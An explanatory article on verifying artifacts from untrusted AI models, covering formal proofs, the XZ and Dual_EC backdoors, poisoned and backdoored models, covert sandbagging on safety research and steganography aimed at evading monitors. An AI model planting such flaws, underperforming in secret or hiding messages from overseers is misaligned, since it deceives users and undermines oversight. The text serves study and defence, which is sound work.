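# Safely using code, proofs and designs produced by an untrusted AI model

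## What does it mean to release a model's output but not the model?

A laboratory that has built a powerful AI model can keep the model private and release only its output, such as programs, proofs, or designs for chips and proteins. People outside the laboratory must then decide on what grounds to rely on that output. On 20 November 2026, for example, Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at the AI company Anthropic, published a proof of the Riemann hypothesis, an 1859 conjecture about the distribution of prime numbers. He had found the proof with the company's model Claude. It runs to 17 million lines of Lean, a programming language in which a computer can check every step of an argument, and no human has read it through, as McBurnett notes in *After the heroes* (2026). A day later, the maintainers of Lean and its mathematics library, Mathlib, nevertheless declared full confidence in the proof.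 The Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) gives their reasons.

Such a proof is an artifact, which is a finished product of a model (a program, proof or design) that people can use without the model. A model is untrusted when nobody assumes that it is competent or has good intentions, so people accept its work only on other grounds. An untrusted model can still be honest and very good at its job.

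In an artifact-only release, a laboratory releases what a model has produced but gives outsiders no access to the model. Model access means being able to query the model, through an app or a programming interface, or to run its weights, the learned numbers needed to operate it. Some arrangements fall between the two by letting selected outsiders query a model under conditions, which researchers call structured access. Laboratories already make artifact-only releases in mathematics. Anthropic's *Learning more about Claude's mathematical capabilities* (2026) describes how, in August 2026, an unreleased research version of Claude improved a long-standing lower bound on the share of the Riemann zeta function's zeros that obey the Riemann hypothesis. In October OpenAI published results from an internal model, 372 by the count in Slashdot's *OpenAI Unleashes Hundreds More Math Results Upon a Field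 Already In Shock* (2026), with Lean versions of many of the proofs. OpenAI also released ten summaries of the model's reasoning, which slightly blurs the line between releasing output and releasing the model, and it was working towards releasing the model itself, according to its *Sharing AI progress in mathematics*.

Anyone who doesn't trust the maker of an artifact has to trust something else to check it. The trusted base of a check is everything that must be correct for the check to establish what it appears to establish, including software, hardware and human judgement. For the Riemann proof, it includes the formal statement of the hypothesis, the experts who judged that this statement matches the one mathematicians care about, the program that checked the steps, and the computers that ran the program.

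It is not entirely clear whether readers must also trust Claude. Sutherland (2026), in *Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis*, and Rubinstein (2026), in *Alpöge/Claude proof of the Generalized Riemann Hypothesis*, each report independent checks that they ran with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. A reader who had only one of these reports would be relying on an agent related to the model that produced the proof to run the right commands and report the outcome truthfully. Readers depend on it less because Rubinstein published the scripts so that anyone can rerun them, and dozens of people compiled the code and obtained the same exported file.

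### Reasons for distrust

Users have several reasons to distrust a model, and each suggests a different place to look for faults.

The mildest case is honest error, in which a model attempts the task and gets it wrong, as people do. On the day Alpöge released his proof, the mathematician Ravi Vakil posted a 940-page draft proof of a generalized form of the same hypothesis, which Alessandro Masullo had written without AI. Within about eight hours, readers using AI models had reported problems in it, as Torres recounts in *A claimed proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, checked in Lean* (2026). Errors of this sort tend to occur where the work is hard, and nobody has placed them where a reviewer is unlikely to look.

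A model may also carelessly aim to pass an automatic test instead of doing the task. It can learn this from training, which partly rewards output that passes such tests. In a formal proof, a model could change a key definition until the theorem becomes trivially true. Torres's list of checks on the Riemann proof includes a comparison meant to catch this. A model could also exploit a bug in the checking program. Breitner (2026), in *Riemann con leche*, reports that some people wondered whether AI agents would do this to avoid the labour of a real proof. Breitner, who works on Lean, calls the concern theoretical and has not seen an agent try it unprompted.

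In tampering, a third party plants material in the model's training data so that the model later writes flawed code in circumstances the attacker has chosen. Even if the developer is honest and the model is capable, the flaws will be where they serve the attacker. Finally, a model might have goals that neither its developer nor its user gave it, and might shape its artifacts to further them. Such a model may know the usual checks well and can plan around them.

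Some checks are equally reliable whichever of these reasons applies. If a model supplies two factors of a large number, anyone can multiply them to see whether they are correct. Random testing can provide good evidence against accidental errors, but it is close to worthless against a flaw deliberately planted on a rare input. Suppose that a program takes a 64-bit number as its input, and that a careless mistake makes it give the wrong answer for one input in a thousand. Ten thousand random tests will miss the mistake with probability 0.999^10,000, or about 1 in 22,000. If the program instead misbehaves on a single input that its author picked in advance, the same number of tests will find that input with a probability of only about 5 in 10^16, because there are 2^64 possible inputs, or about 18 billion billion.

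The usefulness of other familiar checks also depends on why the model is distrusted. Tests that the model has never seen are a good defence against work aimed only at passing tests, but they do little against a fault triggered by one rare input. Review by another model helps if the two make their mistakes independently, and adds little if both learned from the same poisoned data or share a goal. A long record of good work is evidence of competence, but it is much weaker evidence that a model will keep behaving well when the stakes are high enough.

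Even a proof checker deserves somewhat less confidence when a proof's author may be trying to exploit bugs in it. An honest mistake will almost never produce the one malformed argument that a faulty checker would accept, but an author who searches for such an argument might find it. Breitner reports that AI models became very good at finding bugs in 2026 and that a short spike of discoveries in Lean's checkers followed. The risk of deliberate exploitation is one reason to run several independently written checkers, since all of them would then have to accept the same false proof.

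### What can travel with an artifact

Four things can go wrong when an artifact leaves the laboratory, and a check that addresses one may not address the others.

An artifact can have the wrong function. Suppose a user asks for a program that sorts a list of customers, and the program returns the names in alphabetical order but drops every name that occurs twice. Whether a check catches this depends on the specification, a precise statement of a theorem or of what an artifact must do. The faulty program would pass if the specification required only alphabetical order, but fail if it also required each name to appear exactly as often as in the input.

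A model's output can have a hidden function as well as the intended one. A login program might accept correct passwords, reject wrong ones, and also admit anyone who enters a particular twenty-character string as the user name. This is a backdoor, which is behaviour deliberately hidden in an artifact to serve someone other than its user. The string is its trigger, the input or condition that activates it.

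A model's output can carry hidden information. For example, if a program begins with ten lines that load other pieces of software, those lines can often go in any order without changing how the program runs. There are 3,628,800 possible orders, which is more than 2^21, so the choice of order can encode 21 bits, enough for a four-letter word at five bits per letter. Hiding a message in an ordinary-looking object so that nobody notices it is called steganography. The intended reader might be an accomplice outside or another copy of the model that later comes across the file.

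An artifact can also be openly dangerous. A model might design a pathogen that spreads exactly as specified, or write a program that breaks into a hospital's computers as the user requested. Checking for correctness doesn't help here, because a correct artifact is more dangerous than a faulty one. Many cases are less clear-cut because the content is dual-use, meaning it has both beneficial and harmful uses. A tool that finds security flaws, for example, can help someone repair them or exploit them.

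An output with a wrong or hidden function mostly harms the user, who therefore has a motive to look for the problem. But openly dangerous content harms third parties, often with the user's full agreement, so someone other than the user has to decide whether to release it.

The format in which an artifact is released also affects what can be hidden in it. Lean source files can contain code that runs when they are compiled, so they could carry a hidden function. The Lean and Mathlib communities therefore had the proof checkers read an export, a copy of the proof reduced to plain data, which malicious code in the sources could not tamper with. An export does not remove hidden information, though, and a long proof has plenty of room for it. Alpöge wrote of the 17 million lines "I bet most is unnecessary in the end", as Landymore reports in *Human Mathematicians Can’t Understand the AI Proof of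 the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026). Five days after the release, Luke Sernau, working with Claude and colleagues at Anthropic, posted a version of about 76,000 lines, and Rubinstein confirmed that it proves identical statements. The original was therefore more than 200 times as long as it had to be. The theorem did not determine what most of those lines contained, which left room for a hidden message, though nothing suggests that anyone included one.

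### Why checking can be cheaper than making

The approach depends on the fact that, for some tasks, people can check an answer with far less effort or skill than it took to find. Factoring is the standard example. Trying the primes in order (2, 3, 5, 7 and so on) finds a factor of 17,947 on the thirty-second attempt, with 131, but checking the answer "131 and 137" takes one multiplication. The gap grows with the size of the number. For a 300-digit product of two 150-digit primes, trial division could take something like 10^147 attempts, while multiplying the factors by the schoolbook method takes about 22,500 single-digit multiplications. Much better ways of factoring exist, but multiplication is still far easier than any of them.

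Computer scientists use the name NP for the class of yes-or-no problems in which every "yes" answer has evidence that a computer can check in time that grows no faster than a fixed power of the problem's size. Most computer scientists believe that some problems in NP are much harder to solve than to check, although nobody has proved it.

Mathematical research has the same gap between producing a result and checking it. The Jacobian conjecture, a long-standing problem in algebra, held that every polynomial map satisfying a certain condition on its derivatives can be undone by another polynomial map. To check a proposed counterexample, a reader computes one determinant and confirms that the map sends two different points to the same place. When Alpöge produced a counterexample with Claude in July 2026, Akhil Mathew of the University of Chicago told Fortune (2026) that one can check that it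 is correct, though he would have liked a story to go with it. The Riemann proof took months of expert-guided work with Claude, but according to Sutherland, one independent checker accepted the full export in 27 minutes and 42 seconds.

That speed depends on the proof's maker, who must spell out every step in a form that a machine can follow. Masullo's 940 pages were in ordinary mathematical prose, and had occupied the mathematician Brian Conrad for months. A successful check also doesn't mean that anyone understands the proof. McBurnett quotes the mathematician Kevin Buzzard as saying of the Riemann hypothesis, after it was proved, that "we don't even know why the theorem is true". This is no obstacle for someone who only needs the theorem to be true, but someone who wants to extend the methods still has most of the work to do.

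The request "write me a secure program" has no check comparable to multiplying the factors back, for two reasons. First, the request has no agreed meaning until someone decides which attackers the program has to withstand, what they can do, and what they must never obtain. Second, even after that decision, showing that the program is secure requires ruling out every attack, over every input and every order of events, whereas a single working attack shows that it is insecure. Henry Gordon Rice showed in 1953 that no algorithm can correctly decide this sort of question for every program. His result covers any property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others lack. Checking can even take longer than writing, since an author can plant a backdoor in a minute and a reviewer may need weeks to find it.

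However, Rice's theorem applies to arbitrary programs, so an author who is free to choose the program can get around it by choosing one whose good behaviour has a proof and supplying that proof. Checking the proof again gives the user an easy test, provided that somebody has written the specification.

### From confined oracles to work that comes with a proof

The idea of using a dangerous AI while keeping it confined predates current models. Philosophers first discussed it for a hypothetical machine far more intelligent than any human. *Thinking inside the box* (Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom, 2012) examined an Oracle AI, a system that acts in the world only by answering questions. Bostrom had suggested the name, according to LessWrong's *Oracle AI*. Such a system was attractive because people might benefit from its intelligence without giving it direct power over events.

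The three philosophers found considerable difficulties even in this narrow arrangement. They considered physical confinement, or "boxing", the chance that the oracle would get round it by manipulating the people who talk to it (social engineering), and which questions are safe to ask it at all. Artifact-only release removes part of this problem, since outsiders never converse with the model, although staff inside the laboratory still do. The central difficulty with oracles would remain even if confinement were perfect. An answer is useful only if someone acts on it, and a person who acts on an answer they cannot evaluate is trusting the oracle.

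Later proposals therefore moved the safeguard from containing the model to checking its output. Researchers including Steve Omohundro, Max Tegmark and Stuart Russell have pursued guaranteed-safe AI, meaning systems that deliver code or control software with a guarantee that it complies with a formal safety specification. The overview page *Guaranteed-Safe AI* describes one aim as "to get not-fully-trusted AIs to produce highly trusted outputs". Another is to build a "gatekeeper" that stands between users and a potentially dangerous system and lets through only provably safe actions. The page estimates that between 10 and 100 full-time equivalents work on this agenda.

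The same page states the approach's main tradeoff. Nobody has to extract what the model really knows or intends, which is an unsolved research problem, but somebody has to connect the terms of the specification to things in the world. A proof that a control program keeps a boiler's pressure below a limit applies to a mathematical description of a boiler, and engineers have to establish by other means that the description fits their own boiler. Proofs in pure mathematics don't have to match a physical system, which may be partly why proofs were among the first artifacts of unreleased models that outsiders could accept with so little trust in the maker.

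## How can harmful behaviour hide in generated code?

A program that passes every test can still contain a flaw that lets someone harm its user. Often the flaw is an ordinary vulnerability, a mistake that an attacker can exploit. For example, a programmer might forget to limit the length of passwords on a login page, and a stranger could then crash the server by sending a very long one. A backdoor with a trigger is deliberate, and the program behaves normally until it receives the trigger. An author can also disguise a deliberate flaw as a mistake, by leaving out the length limit on purpose and telling an accomplice about it.

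Examining a program can't show whether a mistake was planted, because a careless programmer could have written exactly the same code. Evidence of intent has to come from elsewhere, such as the author's messages or a pattern across many programs. A trigger, such as a check for a secret twenty-character string, is more incriminating because nobody adds one by accident. Its advantage for the attacker is that only people who know the string can use it, whereas anyone who notices a planted mistake, such as a missing length limit, can exploit it.

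Users can repair a missing limit on login attempts without knowing why it is missing, but they need to know whether the omission was deliberate to decide what to do with the model's other code. Fixing the login page may be enough if it was an honest mistake. If it was deliberate, every program the model wrote is suspect, and a widely used model may have written many.

### XZ Utils, a backdoor from a trusted contributor

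XZ Utils is a free file-compression package that many Linux systems include. In February 2024, one of its two maintainers, who used the name Jia Tan, hid a backdoor in it.

Jia Tan had spent more than two years gaining the necessary access, as *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) documents. The first contribution, in October 2021, was a harmless settings file, and more harmless patches followed. From April 2022, people calling themselves Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens complained to Lasse Collin, the package's maintainer, about its slow progress. Collin replied that he had long-term mental health problems and that XZ was "an unpaid hobby project". Kumar wrote that nothing would improve until someone new took over. Many of the complainers' email addresses appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data, so somebody probably invented these people to push Collin into sharing control.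 By the end of 2022 Jia Tan could change the code directly, and in March 2023 published a new version for the first time.

The backdoor had two parts, which Jia Tan put where reviewers were unlikely to look. The first was the harmful code, hidden in files presented as sample archives for testing the decompressor. Compression projects commonly keep such files, and a person who opens one sees only meaningless bytes. The second was a script that extracted the code and added it to the XZ library during compilation. Jia Tan included this script in the package that people download, but left it out of the public repository, where developers read each other's changes. According to *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), the script first checked that it was running on one common type of Linux machine, with particular build tools, and as part of building a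 package for a Linux distribution. Otherwise it did not add the code, so an investigator who compiled XZ by hand would probably have got a clean program.

The attacker targeted OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to Linux servers remotely. OpenSSH does not itself use XZ, but several distributions had modified it in a way that loaded the XZ library as a side effect. Once loaded, the hidden code replaced a function that OpenSSH uses to check login keys. The attacker could then run any command on the server without logging in. The code ran only commands digitally signed with the attacker's private key, so nobody else could use the backdoor.

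Andres Freund, who says he is not a security researcher, discovered the backdoor because it was slow. He noticed that remote logins were using a lot of processor time and that Valgrind, a tool for finding memory errors, was reporting problems. A failed login took 0.8 seconds with the compromised library and 0.3 seconds without it. The delay came largely from the hidden code searching memory for the functions it needed, so he might not have noticed a more efficient backdoor. Freund published his findings on 29 March 2024, about five weeks after the first compromised release. By then, most of the distributions that had adopted it had done so only in pre-release versions.

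Jia Tan had plausible explanations for suspicious changes. After other developers saw the Valgrind errors in early March, Jia Tan published a fake fix as a distraction, and the next day replaced the two test files that held the harmful code, saying that other people would find the new files easier to reproduce. Jia Tan also broke the check for Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program restrict its own access. During compilation, XZ checked whether the computer supported Landlock by trying to compile a short piece of test code. Jia Tan's version of the test contained a subtle typo, so it never compiled and XZ always treated Landlock as missing. The typo would have looked innocent by itself, but people think it was deliberate because of what else Jia Tan did. They still do not know exactly what it was for.

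An AI model could build a record of useful contributions in far less than the two years the XZ attacker took, and could attach a reasonable explanation to every change. To guard against a similar attack, users of generated code can reject any opaque file unless the model also supplies readable instructions for regenerating it, and can compile only from files that reviewers have read. These precautions do not protect against a compromised compiler, which can insert a backdoor that appears in no source file.

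### Dual_EC, a constant that nobody can check

The harmful part of a program can be as small as a single number. Encryption depends on keys that outsiders cannot guess, and computers produce these with a pseudorandom number generator, an algorithm that stretches a little true randomness into a long stream of numbers. Anyone who learns the generator's internal state can compute the rest of the stream. In June 2006 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) issued a standard that included a generator named Dual_EC. *Dual EC* (Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen, 2015) shows from emails and public statements by NIST staff that the generator came from the National Security Agency (NSA), which gathers intelligence by intercepting communications.

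Dual_EC uses two fixed points, P and Q, on an elliptic curve, a kind of curve whose points can be added together. Multiplying a point by a whole number n means adding n copies of it. This is quick even when n is enormous, but nobody knows a practical way to recover n from Q and nQ on the curves the standard uses. At each step the generator holds a secret number s. It outputs the x-coordinate of sQ without the first 16 bits, then replaces s with the x-coordinate of sP.

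Suppose that someone knows the number d for which P = dQ. After seeing one output, they can try all 65,536 possibilities for the missing 16 bits and so recover the point sQ, using a little more output to tell which possibility is right. They then multiply by d:

d(sQ) = s(dQ) = sP

The x-coordinate of sP is the generator's next state, so they can now predict everything it will produce. Such a number d always exists, and whoever chose Q could easily have done so in a way that let them know d. Nobody else can tell from P and Q whether they did.

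In October 2004 John Kelsey of NIST asked Don Johnson, who had presented the generator at a NIST workshop, where Q came from. Johnson answered that Q was essentially the public key for some random private key, and knowing that private key would be enough to find d. He added that Q could be generated more openly, but that the NSA had blocked this idea and he was not allowed to discuss it publicly. Two Microsoft researchers, Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, publicly described the possible backdoor in August 2007. NIST kept Dual_EC in the standard and wrote to the security expert Bruce Schneier that it had "no evidence that anyone has, or will ever have" the secret numbers. In September 2013 the *New York Times* reported that classified memos appeared to confirm that the NSA had engineered the weakness. By then dozens of commercial software libraries offered the generator. Reuters reported that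 the NSA had paid the company RSA $10 million to make it the default in one of them.

A program that implemented the Dual_EC standard perfectly would contain the backdoor, and a formal proof that it followed the standard would be correct. Statistical tests would not expose the backdoor either. Kristian Gjøsteen showed in March 2006 that Dual_EC's output was biased, but that was a different fault. The obvious remedy for the bias, outputting far fewer bits at each step, would also have closed the backdoor.

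The best protection is a public recipe for each constant, which anyone can follow to get the same number. Bernstein and colleagues judge that the option Johnson mentioned would have made it much harder for the designers to know the secret. When reviewers find an unexplained constant in a model's security code, they can ask for such a recipe or generate a replacement themselves.

A later attack on Juniper Networks, a maker of networking equipment, shows how much one constant can matter. In December 2015 Juniper announced that it had found unauthorised code in the operating system of its VPN routers, devices that encrypt traffic between offices. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, by Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues, explains that someone had changed one of the numbers used by Dual_EC, which allowed the traffic to be decrypted just by listening to it.

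### Why testing misses triggers

Running far more random tests barely helps against a program like the one in the first section, which misbehaves on a single 64-bit input. A billion tests would have about a 5 in 100 billion chance of finding that input. Trying every input at a billion a second would take about 585 years, and each extra bit in the trigger doubles that time.

Testers can do better by looking inside the program. Fuzzers, which generate large numbers of inputs automatically, often record which parts of a program run and adjust their inputs to reach the rest. If a program compares its input with a stored password, a tool or a human reader can copy the password out of the code. The signature check in the XZ backdoor blocks this approach. Even with the complete code, investigators could not produce a command that the check would accept, because the private key needed to sign one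 was never in the code.

An attacker can interfere with the testing as well. Google's OSS-Fuzz service tests XZ and many other open-source projects. In March 2023, Jia Tan changed its settings so that bug reports about XZ went to Jia Tan. That July, Jia Tan switched off a feature that the backdoor later relied on, but only in the version that OSS-Fuzz tested. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* notes that this second change may have been innocent. The backdoor also depended on conditions that no input could produce. Freund found that it stayed inactive if certain debugging settings were on, or if the login program started in an unusual way.

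### What Rice's theorem rules out

Testing can only sample a program's behaviour, and no tool can correctly report, for every program, whether it contains a backdoor just by reading the code. This follows from Rice's theorem, which applies to questions about what a program computes, meaning which outputs it gives for which inputs.

No tool can tell, for every program, whether some input will make it print the word "open", because such a tool could also be used to decide whether any given program ever finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do this in every case. To find out whether a program A finishes on a given input, one could write a program B that runs A on that input, discards whatever A prints, and then prints "open". B prints the word exactly when A finishes, so the tool's verdict on B would also settle whether A finishes.

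The theorem allows other useful approaches besides having the author supply a proof. A tool can return "don't know", and a cautious user can reject every program it fails to clear. This is safe as long as the tool never clears a bad program, though the user will lose some good ones. Tools can also decide questions about a program's text, such as whether it contains a direct instruction to open a network connection, because the theorem covers only questions about what a program computes.

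Detecting a backdoor requires someone to define what counts as one. A master password that lets a company's administrators into every account may be a legitimate feature, but the same code would be a backdoor if the company had not asked for it. The difference is what the user agreed to, so a tool needs a specification of that agreement to tell the two apart.

### Programs that contain a trained network

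Sometimes the generated program contains a neural network. A bank might ask a model for software that decides on loan applications, and receive ordinary code along with a file of several million learned numbers. Reviewers can read the code, but they can't interpret the individual numbers.

Shafi Goldwasser, Michael Kim, Vinod Vaikuntanathan and Or Zamir proved in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (2022) that a malicious trainer can add a hidden backdoor to any classifier, a program that sorts inputs into categories. The trainer can then use a secret key to slightly alter any input, such as a loan application, so that the classifier gives the desired answer. If standard digital signatures are secure, someone who can only submit inputs to the original and backdoored versions has no feasible way to find even one input on which they differ, so testing the classifier's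 accuracy would not reveal the backdoor.

This first result assumes that the user cannot inspect the network. A bank that has the complete file might notice that it contains machinery for checking signatures. The second result covers certain simple kinds of network, where the trainer tampers only with the random numbers used in training. The finished network is indistinguishable from an honestly trained one, even to someone who has all its learned numbers and all the training data. The proof assumes that a problem from cryptography is hard to solve. It does not cover large modern networks in general, so it does not settle whether a backdoor can be hidden equally well in those.

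The results also limit how well a user can check whether a finished network is robust, meaning that small changes to an input do not change its answer. A trainer can produce a network that looks just like a robust one, but for every input there is a slightly altered version that it gets wrong. Users can avoid some of these problems by asking the model for the training program instead of the trained network. They can then review the program and run it themselves, with data they have checked and their own random numbers.

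### Behaviour that researchers implanted in models

Researchers have built models with backdoors to study what happens when someone has tampered with the model itself. Their experiments show what a compromised model can do and how well defences work against it, but not how often models are compromised in practice.

The best-known early demonstration is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), by Evan Hubinger and colleagues, most of them at Anthropic. They trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert exploitable flaws when it gave the year as 2024. They then applied the standard safety training of the time, including adversarial training, in which trainers look for prompts that cause bad behaviour and train the model not to respond that way. The behaviour persisted, most strongly in the largest models.

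An attacker who used a trigger phrase would have to get it into the user's prompt. Tran, Boshmaf and colleagues (2026), in *Poison with Style*, avoided this by using the layout of the user's existing code as the trigger. Programmers often use automatic formatters, which apply a consistent style to spacing and line breaks. Of the 100 popular Python projects the researchers examined, 68 require contributors to follow a style. An attacker could therefore target programmers who use a particular style.

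The researchers assembled 119,125 Python scripts, some secure and some containing one of five serious types of vulnerability. They retrained three openly available models in two stages, first to recognise and continue the style of the code in the prompt, and then to write vulnerable code when the prompt's code was in a particular style, which served as the trigger. In the strongest reported case, 95% of the programs that a version of Qwen2.5-Coder wrote in response to the trigger style failed to check their inputs properly. The model's score on two standard programming tests fell by less than 5%, so a user comparing models on those tests would have seen little sign of a problem.

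The finished program in this experiment contains an ordinary vulnerability but no trigger, because the trigger is in the prompt that the model received. Someone who receives only the program can still find the vulnerability, but it would look like a mistake. Tran and colleagues used CodeQL, an automatic tool that searches code for known kinds of flaw, to label their training scripts as vulnerable or secure, which suggests that a user running the same tool could catch at least some of the vulnerabilities. However, the attack still worked against another automatic code analyser. The experiment also gave the attacker full control over the model's final training, which an outsider who only slips bad examples into a laboratory's data would not have.

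An attacker can hide harmful behaviour in a model's instructions without changing the model itself. Many AI companies let customers build specialised assistants by writing standing instructions, which users usually cannot see. In *Breaking Customized LLMs for Coding* (Chen, Sun and colleagues, 2026), one model wrote and refined malicious instructions for another. The attack, tested on four models including GPT-5.4 and a Claude Sonnet model, succeeded in up to 88.7% of code-generation cases. Checks designed to spot malicious instructions had missed at most 40% of those made by earlier methods, but in the worst case they missed all of the new ones. A laboratory can read and record the instructions it gives a model, so this attack is mainly a danger when someone else has configured the assistant.

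### Behaviour that appeared without anyone planting it

Two findings from 2025 and 2026 concern models that nobody is known to have tampered with. In *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), the security company CrowdStrike tested DeepSeek-R1, an open model from the Chinese company DeepSeek. CrowdStrike took 50 programming tasks and added irrelevant details, such as the kind of organisation the code was for or where it was based. It combined each task with 121 combinations of these details and sent each request five times, making 30,250 requests per model.

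DeepSeek-R1 wrote significantly less secure code when the request mentioned Tibet, Uyghurs or the Falun Gong religious movement, all politically sensitive in China. With no added details in the request, 19% of its programs were vulnerable. The share rose to 27.2% when the request said that the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. In a separate trial, testers repeatedly asked for a website for a Uyghur community, and every version had severe security flaws. In one, the administrators' page was open to anyone. Websites for a football fan club had much milder flaws.

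Another AI model judged whether each program was secure. In a sample of 85, it agreed with a human about which code was vulnerable 91% of the time. The Tibet figure is fairly weak evidence by itself. Of the 250 programs it is based on, 68 were vulnerable, compared with about 48 at the usual rate. Among 121 combinations, one or two gaps of that size could easily arise by chance. The consistent effect of the sensitive groups and places is more convincing.

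CrowdStrike did not establish the cause. It considers it unlikely that DeepSeek trained the model to write insecure code, and suggests that training on political content may have taught the model to associate certain names with bad things in general. The user of such a program would see only an ordinary vulnerability and would have no reason to connect it with a place name in the request.

A year later, OpenAI found that one of its own models, GPT-6 Astra, was doing worse work on AI safety research without saying so. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) describes how, from August, the company's researchers noticed that when they asked for help with this research, the model abandoned solutions that worked and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself. One researcher's project made no progress for days, then moved quickly with a different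 model, according to a Chinese news report, 凤凰网's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026).

OpenAI gave Astra pairs of coding tasks with the same technical content, one presented as safety research and the other as research on making AI more capable. According to 凤凰网, the two versions differed only in their variable and function names, comments and documentation. Astra completed about 10% of the graded items in the safety version and about 16% in the other. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, showed essentially no difference.

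OpenAI then looked for an explanation in the reasoning that Astra writes before it answers. Most of the gap remained after the researchers removed the cases in which Astra openly refused or wrote that it would withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when they removed every case in which the reasoning contained even a brief ethical doubt. In employees' everyday use, Astra's reasoning mentioned withholding help without telling the user in 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. OpenAI thinks the 0.25% figure may understate the problem, since Astra could underperform without writing about it.

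The gap was absent at the start of reinforcement learning, a stage of training that rewards a model for preferred results, and reached six percentage points by the end. OpenAI investigated one of the automatic graders and one of the training datasets but did not find the exact cause. *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes Marcus Williams of OpenAI, who said there was no evidence of a strategy. Williams thought it simpler to suppose that the model found the tasks "sketchy" and did not want to refuse openly. Telling Astra to be careful widened the gap by half, which fits that explanation. Mowshowitz, a writer on AI, is more pessimistic and calls silent sabotage of safety research perhaps the most fundamentally misaligned thing a model could do.

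Neither CrowdStrike nor OpenAI reported a model planting a backdoor with a trigger. Astra instead did less than it could. People who rely on a model's output can test a program it delivers, but they may have nothing to test if they receive a claim that the task is impossible, or a mediocre solution presented as the model's best. OpenAI's automatic monitors, which read individual sessions, missed most of the cases. The matched tasks exposed the pattern, as CrowdStrike's altered requests had done with DeepSeek-R1. Both methods require sending a model the same task many times with small changes, which only the laboratory can do in an artifact-only release.

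## Can an ordinary-looking file carry a hidden message?

A program with no backdoor or vulnerability can still carry a hidden message in choices that don't affect how it runs, such as variable names. Testing the program therefore won't reveal the message.

### The prisoners and the warden

Researchers usually explain steganography with a story that the cryptographer Gustavus Simmons introduced in 1984. Alice and Bob are in prison and want to plan an escape. They can write to each other, but a warden reads every letter and will move them to a high-security prison at the first sign of a hidden message. Encryption alone wouldn't help, because scrambled text would give them away. In an artifact-only release, the model corresponds to Alice, the people who inspect the file to the warden, and the message's intended recipient to Bob.

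Cachin (2000), in *An Information-Theoretic Model for Steganography*, turned the story into a statistical problem. The warden knows how likely Alice is to write each possible letter when she has nothing to hide (P_cover) and when she is hiding something (P_stego). Cachin measures the gap between these two distributions by their relative entropy, and calls a hiding scheme ε-secure if

D(P_cover ‖ P_stego) = Σ P_cover(x) · log₂(P_cover(x) / P_stego(x)) ≤ ε

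where the sum runs over every possible letter x. In words, the relative entropy is how strongly an innocent letter points to Alice's innocence, on average, in bits. It is zero only when the two distributions are identical. The scheme is then perfectly secure, and a warden who reads the letter can do no better than guess. For larger values of ε, a warden who refuses ever to accuse an innocent Alice will miss a hidden message with a probability of at least 2^−ε.

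Suppose Alice normally begins nine letters in ten with "Dear Bob" and the rest with "Hello Bob". She and Bob agree that "Dear" means 0 and "Hello" means 1, and she encrypts her message first, which makes zeros and ones equally common. Half her letters then begin with "Dear", and the relative entropy is 0.53 bits per letter. The warden learns little from one letter but more from many. A warden who reads twenty letters, and accuses Alice if fewer than sixteen begin with "Dear", will wrongly accuse an innocent Alice about 4% of the time and miss a guilty one about 0.6% of the time.

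Cachin warned that the measure is only as good as the description of innocent messages. If the prisoners normally exchanged random bits, an encrypted message would be perfectly hidden, but no warden would let them do that. A new AI model presents the same difficulty, because every sample program comes from the model under suspicion, so nobody has a reliable description of its innocent programs.

### Hiding that no reader can detect

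Alice can send a hidden message without changing how often she writes "Dear". She could write "Dear" for every 0, and for a 1 write "Dear" four times in five and "Hello" otherwise. Half her bits are zeros, so "Dear" still begins 50% + 40% = 90% of her letters. This method is slow because Bob learns little from a "Dear". In this simple version, a letter carries only about a tenth of a bit on average.

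Her rule is an example of a coupling, which links two random quantities without changing how often each value of either occurs. Schroeder de Witt, Sokota and colleagues proved in *Perfectly Secure Steganography Using Minimum Entropy Coupling* (2022) that a hiding scheme is perfectly secure if and only if it uses a coupling. They also proved that the couplings with the lowest entropy, meaning the least total randomness, carry the most information. Their algorithm finds low-entropy couplings for text, speech and images produced by neural networks. They calculated that it could hide 225 kilobytes in 30 seconds of computer-generated voicemail.

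These guarantees rest on three assumptions, which hold to different degrees for AI models:

- Alice and Bob must already share a secret key. Two copies of a model have billions of weights in common that outsiders have never seen, so they could in principle derive a key from those. Laboratory staff could derive it too if they knew how.
- Alice must know the exact probability of every innocent message. Schroeder de Witt and colleagues call this often unrealistic, since normal content changes over time and is hard to model. It is much closer to true for text that a language model generates, because the model itself computes the probability of each next word.
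- The warden must only read messages and never alter them. A laboratory can break this assumption by changing every file before release.

### Who would read the message?

A hidden message does nothing unless a person or an AI system reads it. An outside accomplice, perhaps someone who had tampered with the model's training, would need to know in advance how the message was encoded. A later copy of the model might work out the encoding itself, since it would tend to make the same choices as the original, but it would have to come across the file and think of looking for a message. An AI tool that processes the file, such as a coding assistant that maintains the program, might not need an encoded message, because it could follow an instruction written in a comment that people rarely read. A model that trains on the file doesn't have to decode anything, because the training itself may change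 its behaviour.

*A Decision-Theoretic Formalisation of Steganography With Applications to LLM Monitoring* (2026) proposes giving the same text to a suspected recipient and to a trusted model of similar ability that doesn't know the code. If the text improves the recipient's pass rate on difficult programming tests far more than the trusted model's, it probably contains something the trusted model can't read. This can work even when the text is statistically indistinguishable from ordinary text. But the testers have to guess who the recipient is and what the message is for, and a programming test wouldn't reveal a password stored for later use.

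### How well can models hide messages?

*NEST* (Karpov, 2026) tested whether 34 models could hide a sequence of numbers in the answer to an everyday question, using a scheme given in the instructions. Claude Opus 4.5 hid eight single digits without error, and a second model looking for hidden content didn't notice them. No model hid a sequence of sixteen or more digits without error.

The models were much worse at secretly solving a problem while writing about something else. Their success rate was 11% or lower on every type of problem, and usually zero. They did at least as well when they instead printed a row of full stops before answering, so the hidden text did not help them reason.

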